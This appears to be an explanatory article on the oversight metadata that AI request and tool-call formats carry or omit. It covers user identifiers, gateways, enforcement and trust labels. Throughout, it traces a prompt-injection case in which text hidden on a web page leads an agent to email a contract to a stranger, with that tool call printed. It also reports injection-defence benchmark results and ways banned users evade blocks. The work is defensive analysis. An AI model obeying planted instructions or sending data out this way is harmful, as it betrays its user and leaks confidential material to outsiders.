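# Oversight metadata that AI interface standards do not carry

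## How an AI request travels and who monitors it

Oversight metadata is information that accompanies a message to or from an AI system and helps someone check how the system is being used, such as who made a request, where a piece of text came from, or which tool carried out an action. Companies that run AI models need it to catch misuse, and investigators need it to reconstruct incidents. Whether they receive it depends largely on the fixed format in which programs exchange messages with AI models. An interface schema is the published list of fields that these messages may contain. If the schema has no field for a piece of information, whoever had it first usually doesn't pass it on.

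### One request and one tool call

Suppose an employee of a manufacturing firm opens an assistant in a third-party app and asks it to summarise a supplier's web page and email the summary to a colleague, Priya. The app turns this into a message for a model. In OpenAI's Chat Completions format, the message might look like this:

```json
{
  "model": "gpt-6-sol",
  "messages": [
    {"role": "user",
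     "content": "Summarise the supplier's price page and email it to Priya."}
  ],
  "tools": [
    {"type": "function", "function": {"name": "fetch_page"}},
    {"type": "function", "function": {"name": "search_files"}},
    {"type": "function", "function": {"name": "send_email"}}
  ],
  "safety_identifier": "9f2c41d07a",
  "metadata": {"team": "purchasing"}
}
```

The `content` field holds the words that the model will read, `role` marks their author, and `tools` lists the actions the app offers. The last two fields are for record-keeping. `safety_identifier` is a code that stands for the end user, and `metadata` holds up to 16 labelled values that the deployer chooses. Both are optional, since OpenAI's *Create chat completion*, the reference page for the format, requires only `model` and `messages`. A credential travels separately in a header (a line sent ahead of the message body), and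 it does not identify the employee. Open Responses' *Specification*, which defines a newer format, describes this credential as identifying the developer.

A model cannot send an email by itself. It returns a tool call, which consists of a tool's name and some arguments, and another program has to carry it out. If the app reaches its email tool through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), the most widely used open standard for connecting models to tools, that call takes roughly this form:

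```json
{
  "jsonrpc": "2.0", "id": 7, "method": "tools/call",
  "params": {
    "name": "send_email",
    "arguments": {"to": "priya@buyer.example", "body": "Prices rose by..."},
    "_meta": {
      "io.modelcontextprotocol/clientInfo":
        {"name": "desk-assistant", "version": "3.1"},
      "io.modelcontextprotocol/clientCapabilities": {},
      "io.modelcontextprotocol/protocolVersion": "2026-07-28"
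    }
  }
}
```

Here `name` and `arguments` describe the action, and `_meta` holds the metadata. Model Context Protocol's *Overview* (2026), part of the official specification, requires a server to reject any request that lacks the protocol version or the client's capabilities. The client's name and version are optional. The specification reserves no metadata key for the employee, the sentence the employee typed, or the web page the model had just read. An access token sent alongside the message may identify an account to the tool server.

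### How two formats spread

Chat Completions spread without being ratified by a standards body. Developers had already written software for OpenAI's service, and a rival that accepted the same messages could win them as customers without asking them to rewrite it. Developers can switch to Google's Gemini models by changing three lines of code and using a new key, according to Google's *OpenAI compatibility*. TanStack's *OpenAI-Compatible Adapter*, the documentation of a programming toolkit, lists DeepSeek, Moonshot, Perplexity and Alibaba's Qwen among the many providers that accept the format, along with programs such as Ollama that run models on a developer's own machine. Gateways also adopted the format. Cloudflare's *Unified API (OpenAI compat)* documents a single OpenAI-compatible address that leads to several providers.

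OpenAI launched a successor to Chat Completions, the Responses API, in March 2025 and now recommends it for new projects. It also initiated Open Responses, an attempt to make the Responses API an open standard, whose contributors include Nvidia, AWS and Databricks. Yet Hugging Face's *Open Responses* (2026), a post promoting the new standard, conceded that Chat Completions was "still the de facto standard". The developer Simon Willison, in *Open Responses*, welcomed the project but had hoped for a standard based on Chat Completions, because so many products had already cloned it. Some endpoints imitate Anthropic's format instead, and the software company Modular advises developers on using them. An Internet-Draft, IETF's *Multi-Provider Inference API* (2026), compares the Responses API's role to that of HTTP, the protocol of the web. Anyone may submit an Internet-Draft, so this one is evidence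 of a common view among engineers, not of an official decision.

A provider can accept a request format but ignore some of its fields. Anthropic accepts requests in OpenAI's format, mainly so that developers can test its Claude models. Anthropic's *OpenAI SDK compatibility* lists `metadata` as ignored, along with `user`, the older field for an end user's identifier, and most unsupported fields produce no error. Google Cloud also ignores unsupported parameters, according to its *Using OpenAI libraries with Vertex AI*. A deployer that changes provider can therefore keep sending an identifier and getting normal answers without finding out that the new provider discards it.

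For tools, MCP occupies the same position. Google dates MCP's introduction to late 2024, when it suited a single program talking to a single tool server on one machine. By July 2026 the Model Context Protocol (2026) project was reporting close to half a billion downloads a month of its main software development kits (SDKs), the ready-made code that developers build into their products. Anthropic's *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude* (2026) put the figure at over 400 million and reported a fourfold rise within the year. Automated systems download the same SDKs repeatedly, so neither figure is a count of users. Adoption by AWS, Google Cloud, Microsoft and Cloudflare is probably better evidence of MCP's standing. The current version is dated 28 July 2026, and the Model Context Protocol maintainers plan to release the next on 30 March 2027.

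Server operators' needs shaped much of that July version. Google wanted any machine in a large cluster to be able to handle any request, so the maintainers removed the session that tied a client's calls together, and each call now carries its own metadata. They also required clients to copy the tool's name into a header, which lets a gateway route and limit traffic without opening the message. Google points out that this also helps security and logging teams. It is fairly typical for an oversight signal to enter a schema this way, as a field that somebody first needed for traffic or billing.

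### The parties, in order

The employee is the end user. The company that makes the app is the deployer. It holds the employee's login, chooses the tools and composes the messages.

The request may next pass through a gateway, a service that forwards requests to one or more providers. *The Proxy Knows Too Much* (Xie, Wu and colleagues, 2026) describes how one works. The deployer sends its request under a credential that the gateway issued. The gateway picks a provider account from a pool, attaches that account's credential, forwards the request, relays the answer and records how much text the model processed. It closes one encrypted connection and opens another, so every prompt, answer and tool result is readable inside the gateway. The change of credential matters just as much for oversight, because the provider authenticates the gateway's account, and requests from many unrelated people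 can arrive under that account.

Deployers often know little about what happens inside a gateway. *Behavioral Consistency and Transparency Analysis on Large Language Model API Gateways* (2026) lists ways an operator can depart from what it advertises, such as routing a request to a cheaper model or truncating a long prompt.

The model provider runs the model. A tool server then carries out the actions specified in the model's output, in this case fetching a page, searching the firm's files and sending mail. The last party is the affected outsider, anyone who took no part but whose website, inbox or data the action touches. Examples are the supplier and a customer whose details appear in one of the firm's files.

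Some requests pass through fewer parties because the deployer calls the provider directly or the provider runs tools itself. Open Responses distinguishes externally hosted tools, which run outside the provider's systems, from internally hosted ones, which the provider runs without handing control back to the developer. Hugging Face notes that with internal tools, searching documents, summarising them and drafting an email can all happen in one request. The provider then has the fullest record of the work. With external tools, it has only the calls its model produced and any results returned to it.

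### Four kinds of monitor

A monitor is any person or program that checks AI activity for misuse, error or rule-breaking, either as it happens or afterwards. Four kinds of monitor matter here, and the activity they can see overlaps less than one might expect.

The provider's abuse detection can examine everything that enters and leaves the model and compare patterns across thousands of deployers. OpenAI describes the `safety_identifier` as helping to detect users who may be breaking its policies, which implies that it wants to look at individuals as well as whole accounts. It can do that only if the deployer supplies the identifier. The provider also doesn't know the setting, so it can't tell whether an address in an email call belongs to a colleague or a thief.

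A deployer running its own checks knows which employee logged in, what that employee may open, and often what the tools did, but its logs of model calls can contain little detail. OpenTelemetry's *Semantic conventions for generative client AI spans*, part of a widely used open standard for software logs, covers the model requested, the model that answered, the amount of text and any error. Prompts, answers and system instructions are opt-in, with a warning that they may contain sensitive information. A deployer that keeps the default settings can tell when a call took place and how long the answer was, but not what the employee asked for. The provider's name in the log is also a best guess, because a service that accepts OpenAI's format may pass requests to another provider.

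An auditor or incident investigator usually arrives later and has only the records that the other parties kept and will hand over. The work is mostly matching those records, such as a line in the app's log with a charge in the gateway's accounts and an email in the tool server's outbox. Without a shared identifier, the investigator has to match them by time and content, which becomes unreliable when an app makes thousands of similar calls an hour.

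The outsider has the least information. The supplier's web server receives a page request, and a mail server receives an email. Neither receives the model request or the MCP call, so adding a field to those messages would not help the outsider unless somebody also copied the field's contents into the web request or the email.

### Four states of a signal

In a given schema, any fact that a monitor might want will be in one, or sometimes two, of the following states.

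- No field. The schema has no agreed place for the fact. When an app returns a web page to the model in Chat Completions, the message has fields for the text, the role and the tool call it answers, and none for the page's address. A company may add a field of its own, but Open Responses advises implementers to treat such additions as vendor-specific and not to assume that other services will recognise them.
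- Optional field. The place exists, and a sender may leave it empty without breaking any rule. The `safety_identifier` is an example. When it is missing, a monitor cannot tell whether the deployer has no such code, chose not to send it, or lost it on the way.
- Self-reported field. The sender fills in the value and nobody checks it. MCP's client name is self-reported, and the Model Context Protocol specification advises against relying on it for security decisions. A malicious program can call itself `desk-assistant` as easily as the real one.
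- Verified field. The receiver can check the value. The credential on a model request belongs here, because the provider can compare it with its own records.

"Optional" means a value may be missing, while "self-reported" and "verified" describe how much to trust a value that is present. MCP's client name is both optional and self-reported.

Verification between organisations mostly relies on hashes and digital signatures. A hash is a short code computed from a piece of data. The same data always gives the same code, and finding different data that gives the same code is practically impossible, so anyone who has the hash can test whether a copy has changed. A digital signature also ties the data to a signer, who computes the signature with a secret key. Anyone with the matching public key can check that the holder of the secret key signed exactly that data.

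A hash alone gives limited protection. In November 2026, the Model Context Protocol maintainers described a draft extension for file transfers that includes an optional hash of the file. The hash would expose a damaged upload, but if someone replaced both the file and its hash, the receiver would need a signature or a hash obtained by another route to detect the change. Xie and colleagues combine a signature and a hash in their design for a safer gateway. The forwarding program runs in a sealed area of the processor, which issues a signed document containing a hash of that program. The client checks the signature and compares the hash with the one it expects before releasing the prompt. They note that this proves which program is running, but not that the program is harmless. Verified fields in general have similar limits. For example, a valid signature on a request to send an email shows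 who signed the request, but not whether the employee wanted the email sent.

### The supplier's page

The employee's app sends the request through a gateway to the model, which calls `fetch_page`. The tool server retrieves the supplier's page, and the app passes its text to the model. Somebody has hidden an instruction on the page, in white letters on a white background, for any AI assistant to find the firm's latest supplier contract and send it to an outside address. This attack is called prompt injection. It hides instructions in content that a model reads, to make the model act for someone other than its user. It can work because the model receives the employee's request and the page as text in the same conversation, and nothing in the page's text reliably separates information from instructions.

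The model calls `search_files`, then `send_email` with the contract attached and a stranger's address in the `to` field. It then writes the summary and emails it to Priya. Every message satisfies its schema, and the employee gets what they asked for and notices nothing.

A monitor who came across the stray email, that day or three months later, would have seven questions:

1. Which person was behind the request, and has the same person turned up in other incidents?
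2. Which of the texts in front of the model had the authority to give it instructions, and did the page have any?
3. Which tool sent the email, who operates that tool, and what else could it have done?
4. Where did the planted sentence come from, and where did the attached file come from?
5. Had a filter or a reviewer at any of the companies already flagged the page, the request or the account?
6. Which model calls and tool calls belonged to this one task, and in what order did they happen?
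7. Whose agent visited the supplier's site and wrote to the stranger, and what had that person or company allowed it to do?

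## Identifying the end user

The first question about the stray email was who was behind the request. The deployer can look the employee up in its login records, but the provider has only the code that the deployer sent, `9f2c41d07a`. This is a pseudonymous identifier, a stable code that stands for a person without naming them. The provider can use it to find the deployer's other requests for the same employee, but would have to ask the deployer for the employee's name.

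### From one field to two

OpenAI's older field for this code, `user`, also affected what a deployer paid. Providers cache (keep a processed copy of) the opening of recent prompts and charge less when another prompt begins with the same text, provided the new request reaches a machine that holds the copy. OpenAI explained in a forum announcement, *Prompt Cache Routing + the `user` Parameter*, that it chose the machine by organisation and by roughly the first 256 tokens (word fragments) of the prompt, and that a `user` value could improve this routing.

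The two purposes could conflict. A developer who replied to the announcement described a product whose users all share one long opening prompt. Sending a different `user` value for each person could scatter their requests across machines and lose the discount, so a deployer might pay more for identifying its users. The same developer said that readers who had never heard of a user ID preventing a ban could decide for themselves whether to send one.

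OpenAI has since split the field into `prompt_cache_key`, which it describes as an optional value for improving cache use, and `safety_identifier`, which is for detecting abuse. A deployer can now give all its users one cache key and keep their safety identifiers separate. Developers choose the cache key to suit their traffic, so it is poor evidence of who sent a request, since it may represent one person in one product and every user in another.

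### What deployers send

OpenAI's *Safety best practices* recommends the optional `safety_identifier` for products in which individuals interact with a model. OpenAI's *How to Incorporate a Safety Identifier* asks for a string unique to each user and advises hashing the username or email address so that OpenAI receives no identifying information, though a hash hides an email address less well than this implies. For visitors who haven't logged in, a deployer can send a session ID. OpenAI's *Create a model response* limits the identifier to 128 characters. Open Responses' *Reference Endpoints* also lists `safety_identifier` and `prompt_cache_key` as optional.

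OpenAI warns that identifiers don't carry over between its interfaces or between sessions, so an app that identifies its users in text requests must send the same code again when it generates an image or opens a voice session. Voice sessions take the code in a header instead of the message body. The embeddings interface, which turns text into numbers for search, has no `safety_identifier` field and still uses `user`.

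Anthropic's equivalent, `metadata.user_id`, is also optional and comes from the deployer. Anthropic asks for a random code, hash or other opaque value, and tells deployers to leave out names, email addresses and phone numbers. It says it may use the value to help detect abuse.

The large cloud platforms mostly seem to pass on the model maker's own field. The software company Vercel runs a gateway that accepts one identifier and translates it for each provider, and Vercel's *AI Gateway Safety Identifiers* sets out where the value goes. OpenAI's models receive it as `safety_identifier`, including when Microsoft's Azure or Amazon's Bedrock serves them. Anthropic's models receive it as `metadata.user_id`, including on Bedrock and on Google's Vertex. Models that Meta serves take `safety_identifier`. Google's Gemini models are not on the list, so a deployer that moves its traffic to Gemini through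 this gateway shouldn't count on the identifier arriving. (Gateways can also garble identifiers, one of several faults that arise in transit.)

All of these values are self-reported, so the provider can't verify that two requests with the same code came from the same person.

### Linking, warning and blocking

OpenAI uses an automated classifier to grade requests to GPT-5 by risk. If an organisation's requests repeatedly reach a high grade, OpenAI returns an error and emails a warning. If such requests continue past a stated period, usually seven days, it ends the organisation's access to the model. OpenAI's published criteria for blocking individual identifiers currently concern suspicious biological or chemical activity.

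Identifiers let OpenAI act against a single user. Its mildest step is to withhold the answer while it runs further checks, and the user receives nothing if the request fails them. When OpenAI is highly confident that someone has broken its policies, it blocks their identifier, and every later GPT-5 request under that identifier returns an error. Deployers can have the notices sent to their own investigators, who can match the identifier to a login.

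OpenAI says it currently cannot unblock an individual identifier. A deployer that believes the block was a mistake could give the person a new code, but to OpenAI this would look exactly like evading the block.

The rules for cyber activity are milder. Under OpenAI's *Cybersecurity checks*, a deployer that sends no user identifiers may temporarily lose access for its whole organisation. If it sends an identifier for each user, OpenAI may suspend only the affected user, after human review and warnings. The deployer can then ask OpenAI to restore access before a seven-day period ends.

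Blocking an identifier stops a determined person only if the deployer helps. OpenAI tells deployers to prevent blocked users from opening new accounts, and warns that the whole organisation can still lose access after repeated violations. If the deployer makes the identifier by hashing an email address, a new address produces a new identifier with no history. If the identifier is a session ID, starting a new session may be enough. OpenAI therefore suggests requiring a login, perhaps through an existing Gmail or LinkedIn account, and notes that asking for a credit card or ID card lowers the risk further. *Build with child safety in mind*, OpenAI's guidance on child safety, also mentions device IDs as a way to recognise people who return after a ban.

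Returning users make enforcement statistics hard to interpret. Anthropic banned 11.4 million accounts between January and June 2026, according to its *System Trust and Reporting* (2026), up from the 1.45 million it reported in January for the previous six months. Because these figures count accounts rather than people, someone banned six times would add six to the total. The nearly eightfold rise could therefore reflect more offenders, more persistent ones, better detection or a mixture.

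In the case of the supplier's page, a block would also affect the wrong person. The requests used to steal the contract carried the employee's identifier, although the instruction came from text hidden on the page. A provider that saw only a suspicious email under `9f2c41d07a` might suspend the employee, who was the victim. The identifier shows on whose behalf a request was made, so the provider needs other fields to find the cause.

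### Why the history matters

Someone can spread misuse over many requests that each look like ordinary work, so that only the full set reveals the purpose. A monitor that judges requests one at a time will miss this.

Anthropic's Frontier Red Team, which studies dangerous uses of AI, assessed misuse by actor. It found that the highest-risk actors differed from the rest in the techniques they asked for help with, but not in whether they reached the model through an API or a coding product. Measuring the range of techniques an actor asks about requires their whole history, so a provider can only do it if it knows which requests came from the same actor.

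The team expects this signal to weaken as AI-assisted techniques spread and more people ask for the same things. It thinks the better indicator will be the software an actor builds around a model to chain the stages of an attack together, and it cites an espionage campaign that Anthropic disrupted in November 2025 as an early case. Linking requests would probably still be useful, because a single request doesn't show a chain of automated stages either.

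A provider's record of a person covers only their use of its own models. The law firm Mishcon de Reya cautions in *Anthropic's first year of AI threat intelligence rewrites the attacker risk model* that skilled attackers may choose open models or other providers to avoid Anthropic's monitoring, so Anthropic's data likely understates what they do. If someone divides a project between two providers, each has only part of the record, and the codes they receive for that person need not match.

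### Ten thousand people under one identifier

Suppose, using invented figures, that a reseller buys access to a model and serves 10,000 people under a single identifier. Each person makes 20 requests a day, and the provider's classifier wrongly flags one in 10,000 harmless requests. Even if every customer is honest, the reseller's 200,000 daily requests will produce 20 false alarms under that identifier.

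If five of the 10,000 people misuse the model, and each makes four requests a day that the classifier correctly flags, the daily count of flagged requests under the shared code rises from 20 to 40. The provider can see the increase, but not that five people caused it. It can block the code, which also cuts off 9,995 people who did nothing wrong, or it can keep serving the five.

With one code per person and the same classifier, an honest customer would trigger a false alarm about once in 500 days. Someone with four flagged requests a day would stand out at 2,000 times that rate, and the provider could block five codes.

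On 20 October 2026, Anthropic began letting platforms, gateways and resellers register a user profile for each end customer, so that an enforcement action can apply to one customer instead of the whole organisation (*Claude Platform release notes*, 2026). The reseller creates the profile once and then sends its ID with each request in the `anthropic-user-profile-id` header. A day later, Anthropic added fields that let the reseller check whether Anthropic has restricted or banned a customer. Automatic notices of these decisions are in beta, and resellers must request access.

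A profile can represent either a person or a company. Anthropic's *Create User Profile* distinguishes `application`, for an individual user of a product, from `passthrough`, for a company to which the platform resells access. With a `passthrough` profile, the choice is still between blocking everyone and blocking no one, but only within that company. If the company has 400 staff, banning its profile blocks all 400.

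Honest resellers have a reason to use profiles that illicit ones lack, because separating their customers protects the rest of their business. On 24 November 2026 Britain's National Cyber Security Centre reported a marked rise since September in cyberattacks assisted by AI. It linked attackers' falling costs largely to widely available hacking software combined with cheap open models or "illegal API resellers", as Martin reported in *UK cyber agency seeing ‘marked rise’ in AI-driven attacks* (2026). Such a reseller can leave out the identifier or invent a new code for every request. Inventing codes is worse for a monitor than using a single shared code, because each request then appears to come from a new person with no history.

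A provider has to rely on what it can verify to stop such resellers, chiefly the account and its credential. OpenAI tells developers to revoke any key they believe has been exposed or misused. In November 2026 Anthropic began letting organisations list the network addresses it should accept their requests from, which limits where a thief can use a leaked key. These measures make stolen access harder to resell, but they do not identify the buyers. They also have no effect on open models that attackers run on their own machines, because no provider receives those requests.

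### Facts that have no common field

Even an honest, consistent identifier tells a provider very little about the person. Four missing facts matter most for oversight.

The `safety_identifier` and `metadata.user_id` fields do not show whether anyone checked the person's identity. A deployer that inspected a passport can send a code that looks like one from a deployer that accepts any email address. The fields also have no place for an age band, so a provider that wanted to treat a 12-year-old's questions differently from a teacher's would have to guess from the text or rely on the deployer's own controls.

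Interface standards also don't carry the person's role or any professional authorisation. A tester hired by a bank to break into its systems may ask for the same help as a criminal with the same target. If the techniques people request are the best available sign of risk, as the Frontier Red Team found, legitimate security staff will look like a provider's most dangerous users.

A deployer also cannot state in these fields that two identifiers belong to one person. This affects people who return after a ban and anyone who uses two apps built on the same model, since each app makes its own identifiers.

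Anthropic's user profiles can hold somewhat more information. Besides a reference code, a profile has fields for the customer's country, account status, entity type and sign-up date, and for hashes of the email address and name. The sign-up date would help a monitor spot a day-old account. A monitor could also use the email hash to detect the same address on two platforms, if both hash it the same way. No standard field covers age, profession or an identity check. A platform could add these facts using a profile's 16 free-form labels, but those labels have no agreed meaning.

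Every detail in a user profile is optional, and the sample code in Anthropic's documentation creates a profile with no details. Anthropic's *User Profiles* states that Anthropic does not verify what platforms enter.

### Verified access outside the schema

For a few sensitive capabilities, providers themselves now check people and organisations. They check once, before any request, and attach the result to an account.

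Anthropic's *Cyber Verification Program* offers three tiers of access to models with relaxed safeguards for security work. Defense Access covers tasks such as malware analysis and incident response, and individuals can apply for it. Red Team Access covers authorised break-in tests and the development of attack tools, and only organisations can apply. Specialized Access is for teams that test systems such as power grids, and Anthropic reviews those applications with the US government.

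Individuals need a government photo ID and may have to take a live selfie. Organisations supply their legal name, address and registration number. Applicants for Red Team Access must also show that they do red-team work professionally, for example through staff certifications, a testing accreditation or a redacted test report. No request field carries this evidence of role.

An administrator then turns on the access for a particular workspace (a subdivision of an API account) or, on enterprise plans, for a particular role. Red Team Access allows up to 75 approved users and Specialized Access up to 25. Anthropic also controls the credentials, because an approved account would be valuable to a thief. Defense Access currently accepts only API keys that expire within seven days. From 15 December 2026 it will accept no API keys, and applicants will have to use short-lived credentials tied to their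 own login systems.

OpenAI runs a similar programme called Daybreak, which it describes as having a Blue tier for defensive work and a Red tier for advanced work such as developing proof-of-concept exploits and penetration testing. According to OpenAI's *Enterprise Daybreak onboarding*, the verification company Persona checks the business, OpenAI does its own review, and an account owner enables access for chosen projects or users.

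Daybreak does add a field to the request. In the Responses API, a deployer sets `access_programs.cyber` to `daybreak_blue`, `daybreak_red` or `standard`. This selects a level of access, but OpenAI checks the setting against the approval it holds for that project, so the field alone doesn't prove a right to that access. Chat Completions doesn't support this route for at least one current model, GPT-6.1 Terra.

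Both companies restrict resale. Customers may use Daybreak only for internal work, and OpenAI's *Trusted Access for Cyber* forbids sharing access with third parties or selling it to them. Anthropic accepts applications from security firms whose staff use Claude on a client's behalf, and from makers of defensive products in which customers can't direct the model. It doesn't yet let an approved company extend its access to customers who write their own prompts.

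These programmes give a provider better evidence than any self-reported field could, but they cover few people and the result stays with that provider. An approval from Anthropic has no effect at OpenAI, and when an approved tester's agent sends a command to a tool server, nothing in the command shows the approval. When a provider grants access to a whole project, it knows only that the project qualified and depends on the customer to keep everyone else out. Extending identity checks to ordinary users would meet resistance. Business Today's *Anthropic may ask for your ID to use Claude* (2026) recorded a backlash on social media after Anthropic began asking some Claude users for an ID and camera access in April 2026.

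User profiles partly connect these checks to individual requests. A platform can send its customer a link to Anthropic's verification portal, where the customer applies directly. Anthropic then records the outcome on the customer's profile as a trust grant, for instance `cyber`, with the status active, pending or rejected. The platform can't award the grant itself, so the grant is a verified fact about the profile. But the platform still decides which profile ID to attach to each request. If it attached an approved tester's ID to a stranger's prompt, by mistake or for money, the header would look the same as it does on the tester's own requests.

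## Marking which text the model may obey

The monitor's second question about the stray email was which texts had the authority to give the model instructions. The model had read the employee's request, the supplier's page and one of the firm's contracts. In most schemas, the only field relevant to this question is `role`.

### Message roles

In Chat Completions, a `system` message (`developer` for newer models) holds the deployer's standing instructions. A `user` message holds the end user's input, an `assistant` message holds the model's earlier output, and a `tool` message holds what a tool returned. Developers also use these roles to rank instructions. The deployer's instructions outrank the end user's, and a tool result has no authority of its own, so the model should treat any instruction in it as information.

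The format does not enforce this ranking. Software joins all the messages into one sequence of tokens, with a marker where each message begins, and the model reads the whole sequence. Developers train the model to rank messages by their markers, using conversations in which two messages conflict and rewarding answers that follow the higher-ranked one. The trained model usually follows the ranking, but may not do so on text unlike the training examples.

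Models differ widely in how often they obey instructions planted in tool results. *MetaPermit* (Ma, Hariri and colleagues, 2026) tested two open-weight models on 7,545 simulated attacks of this kind each. With no defence beyond its training, Qwen3-235B carried out the attacker's task in 26.5% of cases overall, and in almost half of those set in a simulated Slack workspace. The newer MiniMax-M2.7 did so in 2.9% of cases overall. The attacks came from five fixed templates, so an attacker who adapted the wording to the model would probably succeed more often.

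The deployer's setup can also affect whether an agent obeys planted text. Ouyang and Hou (2026), in *Memlineage*, gave OpenAI's gpt-5.3-codex six simulated banking tasks with planted instructions, and the attack succeeded in one. When they configured the agent to trust workflow records in tool results and made the planted text look like such a record, the attack succeeded in all six. A deployer could easily write a similar instruction for a good reason, for example in an agent that works through support tickets.

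Even a model that followed the ranking perfectly would lack some of the facts it needs, because roles are so coarse:

- The supplier's page and the firm's own contract both arrive as `tool` messages.
- If the employee pastes an email from the supplier into the chat, it arrives under `user`, with the same rank as the employee's own words.
- If the model summarises the page, the summary has the role `assistant`, and nothing marks it as web content.
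- A search of an inbox can return a colleague's message and a stranger's in a single `tool` message.

Roles also carry no information about who may read a text, which matters as soon as the model can send email.

### Trust labels and how they spread

A trust label on a piece of content indicates how far the content's source may be relied on or obeyed. Engineers usually pair it with a sensitivity label, which lists who may see the content. Information-flow control, an old security technique, tracks both labels as data moves through a program. Microsoft's *Information-flow control* adapts this technique to agents. The agent's software labels all incoming data, carries the labels over to anything the agent produces from that data, and checks them against a policy before each tool call.

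The rule for carrying labels over is that an output takes the lowest trust and the highest sensitivity of its inputs. If trust has two values, with untrusted below trusted, and each text has a set of permitted readers, then for an output made from texts *a* and *b*:

- trust(output) = min(trust(*a*), trust(*b*))
- readers(output) = readers(*a*) ∩ readers(*b*)

In Microsoft's example of the second line, which involves no attacker, Alex asks an assistant to answer some emails. One is from a colleague and previews the quarterly sales figures. Another is from Marco, who is curious about the figures but not yet entitled to see them. Only Alex may read both emails, so only Alex may read a reply based on both, and the assistant can't send that reply to Marco by itself. It could do so if the colleague had copied Marco on the email with the figures.

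The rule assumes that every text the model has read influenced everything it wrote afterwards. This is often false, but it is hard to tell from outside which parts of its context the model used.

A policy then determines what an agent may do with each label. Microsoft's sample policy for posting to a chat channel allows the post if the context is trusted or if everyone in the channel may already read the content. Otherwise, the user must approve the post. A person can therefore share something confidential on purpose, but text planted on a web page can't cause that without the person's approval. The table applies this policy to the employee's task, assuming that the request itself contains nothing confidential and that Priya belongs to the purchasing team.

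| Step | Label on the new text | Label on the whole context | Outcome |
|---|---|---|---|
| Employee types the request | trusted, public | trusted, public | |
| `fetch_page` returns the supplier's page | untrusted, public | untrusted, public | |
| `search_files` returns the contract | trusted, purchasing team | untrusted, purchasing team | |
| `send_email` to the stranger | | untrusted, purchasing team | Held, and the employee is asked |
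| `send_email` to Priya | | untrusted, purchasing team | Sent |

Microsoft puts the labels in the `_meta` part of an MCP call, where software that doesn't recognise them can ignore them. In its format, the call to the stranger would look roughly like this, with `$` standing for the whole call:

```json
{
  "name": "send_email",
  "arguments": {"to": "stranger@elsewhere.example", "body": "..."},
  "_meta": {
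    "com.github.ifc/labels": {
      "$": {"integrity": "untrusted",
            "confidentiality": ["employee-id", "priya-id"]}
    }
  }
}
```

Three months later, this record would still show a monitor that the agent had read untrusted text before writing the email and that the recipient was not entitled to the contents. Without the labels, the call would show only an address and a body.

### After one web page, everything is untrusted

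In the table, the context becomes untrusted when the page arrives and stays that way. The sample policy allows this, but Microsoft also describes a stricter one, under which untrusted data can never influence a consequential action. That would block prompt injection, but it would also block the email to Priya, even if the page were harmless, because the summary comes from the page. An agent that reads the web, an inbox or customer tickets will have an untrusted context most of the time.

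Sensitivity spreads in the same way. If Priya worked in accounts and had no access to the contract, the milder policy would also delay her summary, even though it contains only public prices. The attacker would have caused the delay just by getting the agent to open the file.

Ouyang and Hou measured this drawback on 13 scripted actions that combined trusted and untrusted text. A rule that judged the context as a whole let none of them through. Rules for individual arguments let nine through and still blocked every value the attacker had supplied. Such a rule names the sources that may supply a particular argument, so a trusted bill can determine who receives a payment but a to-do item from outside can't. For the employee's emails, the deployer could require the `to` address to come from the employee's request or the firm's address book, and let the body come from anywhere. The summary would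 then reach Priya, while an email to the stranger would be blocked. Thirteen scripted cases can show that the method works, but they don't measure how often real tasks need it.

Another way to limit the spread is to keep untrusted text away from the model that chooses the actions. Microsoft's Agent Framework, a toolkit for building agents, can store an untrusted result in a variable that the main model doesn't read. The main model can send questions about it to a second, quarantined model, which has no tools. For the supplier's page, the quarantined model would write the summary, and the main model would put it in the email to Priya without reading it. The planted sentence could spoil the summary, but it couldn't start a file search or choose a recipient. The main model can also request the text itself, but its context then becomes untrusted.

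CaMeL, a 2025 research system, relies on the same separation. Its planning model writes the task as a program, and the system tracks which data may flow into which step. Ma and colleagues cite a result in which CaMeL completed 77% of tasks on AgentDojo, a standard benchmark of simulated office, travel, banking and Slack work. Almost no attacks succeeded, and it used 2.8 times the usual number of tokens. When they ran CaMeL themselves on AgentDojo and AgentDyn, a newer set of more open-ended tasks, it completed a much smaller share. The table gives the averages they measured under attack for CaMeL and for their own system, MetaPermit.

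| | Qwen3-235B: attacks that succeeded | Qwen3-235B: tasks completed | MiniMax-M2.7: attacks that succeeded | MiniMax-M2.7: tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| No defence | 26.5% | 62.4% | 2.9% | 62.8% |
| CaMeL | 0.5% | 42.2% | 0.3% | 25.8% |
| MetaPermit | 0.0% | 50.1% | 0.1% | 53.9% |

CaMeL's average combines very different results. It completed 74% of simulated office tasks with Qwen3, compared with 65% for the undefended agent, but none of AgentDyn's shopping, GitHub and daily-life tasks with either model. Those tasks often require the agent to read something before it can know the next step, and some of the third-party instructions it encounters are useful. Ma and colleagues were testing a competitor, and used open-weight models, so their figures may understate what CaMeL can do. But a score of zero on three sets of tasks is hard to attribute to the choice of model.

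Products have only begun to use labels. GitHub's MCP server can attach them to its results if the client sends a particular header, and GitHub's Copilot command-line agent will act on them if the user turns on an experimental setting. The agent doesn't yet cover all of the server's tools, or any other server. Microsoft reports no attack or completion rates for these prototypes. The labels are also only guesses, because the server marks all files from public repositories as untrusted and all files from private ones as trusted. If a colleague copies a stranger's text into a private file, the server will wrongly mark it as trusted.

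### SEP-1913

Microsoft's labels use a key that other companies' software has no reason to look for. Specification Enhancement Proposal (SEP) 1913, *Trust and Sensitivity Annotations*, would give MCP a common set of labels. SEPs are the formal way to change the protocol. Sam Morrow of GitHub and Robert Reichel of OpenAI wrote this one, and the Model Context Protocol (2026) project says they were responding to gaps they had found while running MCP in production.

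The proposal labels the data that a tool returns. MCP's existing annotations describe the tool and stay the same whatever it fetches. Morrow's commit message of 27 November 2025, which appears in the discussion of the related proposal *SEP-1862*, lists five fields for results. The table shows plausible values for the supplier's page and the contract, and the label the session would have after both.

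| Field | What it marks | Supplier's page | Contract | Session |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| `sensitiveHint` | How sensitive the data is | low | high | high |
| `privateHint` | Whether the data is private | false | true | true |
| `openWorldHint` | Whether it came from outside a closed system | true | false | true |
| `maliciousActivityHint` | Whether the server suspects an attack | false | false | false |
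| `attribution` | Where the data came from | supplier's site | file store | both |

The last column follows the proposal's rules for accumulation. Sensitivity can rise during a session but never fall. Once any result sets a true-or-false field to true, it stays true for the session, and sources accumulate in `attribution`. The client then attaches labels to its later requests, so the server that sends email can detect that the session has already handled private data and text from the open web. Simon Willison calls the combination of private data, untrusted content and a way to send messages out the "lethal trifecta", because together they are enough for data theft. If the labels show the first two, the client could block the email tool or ask the employee.

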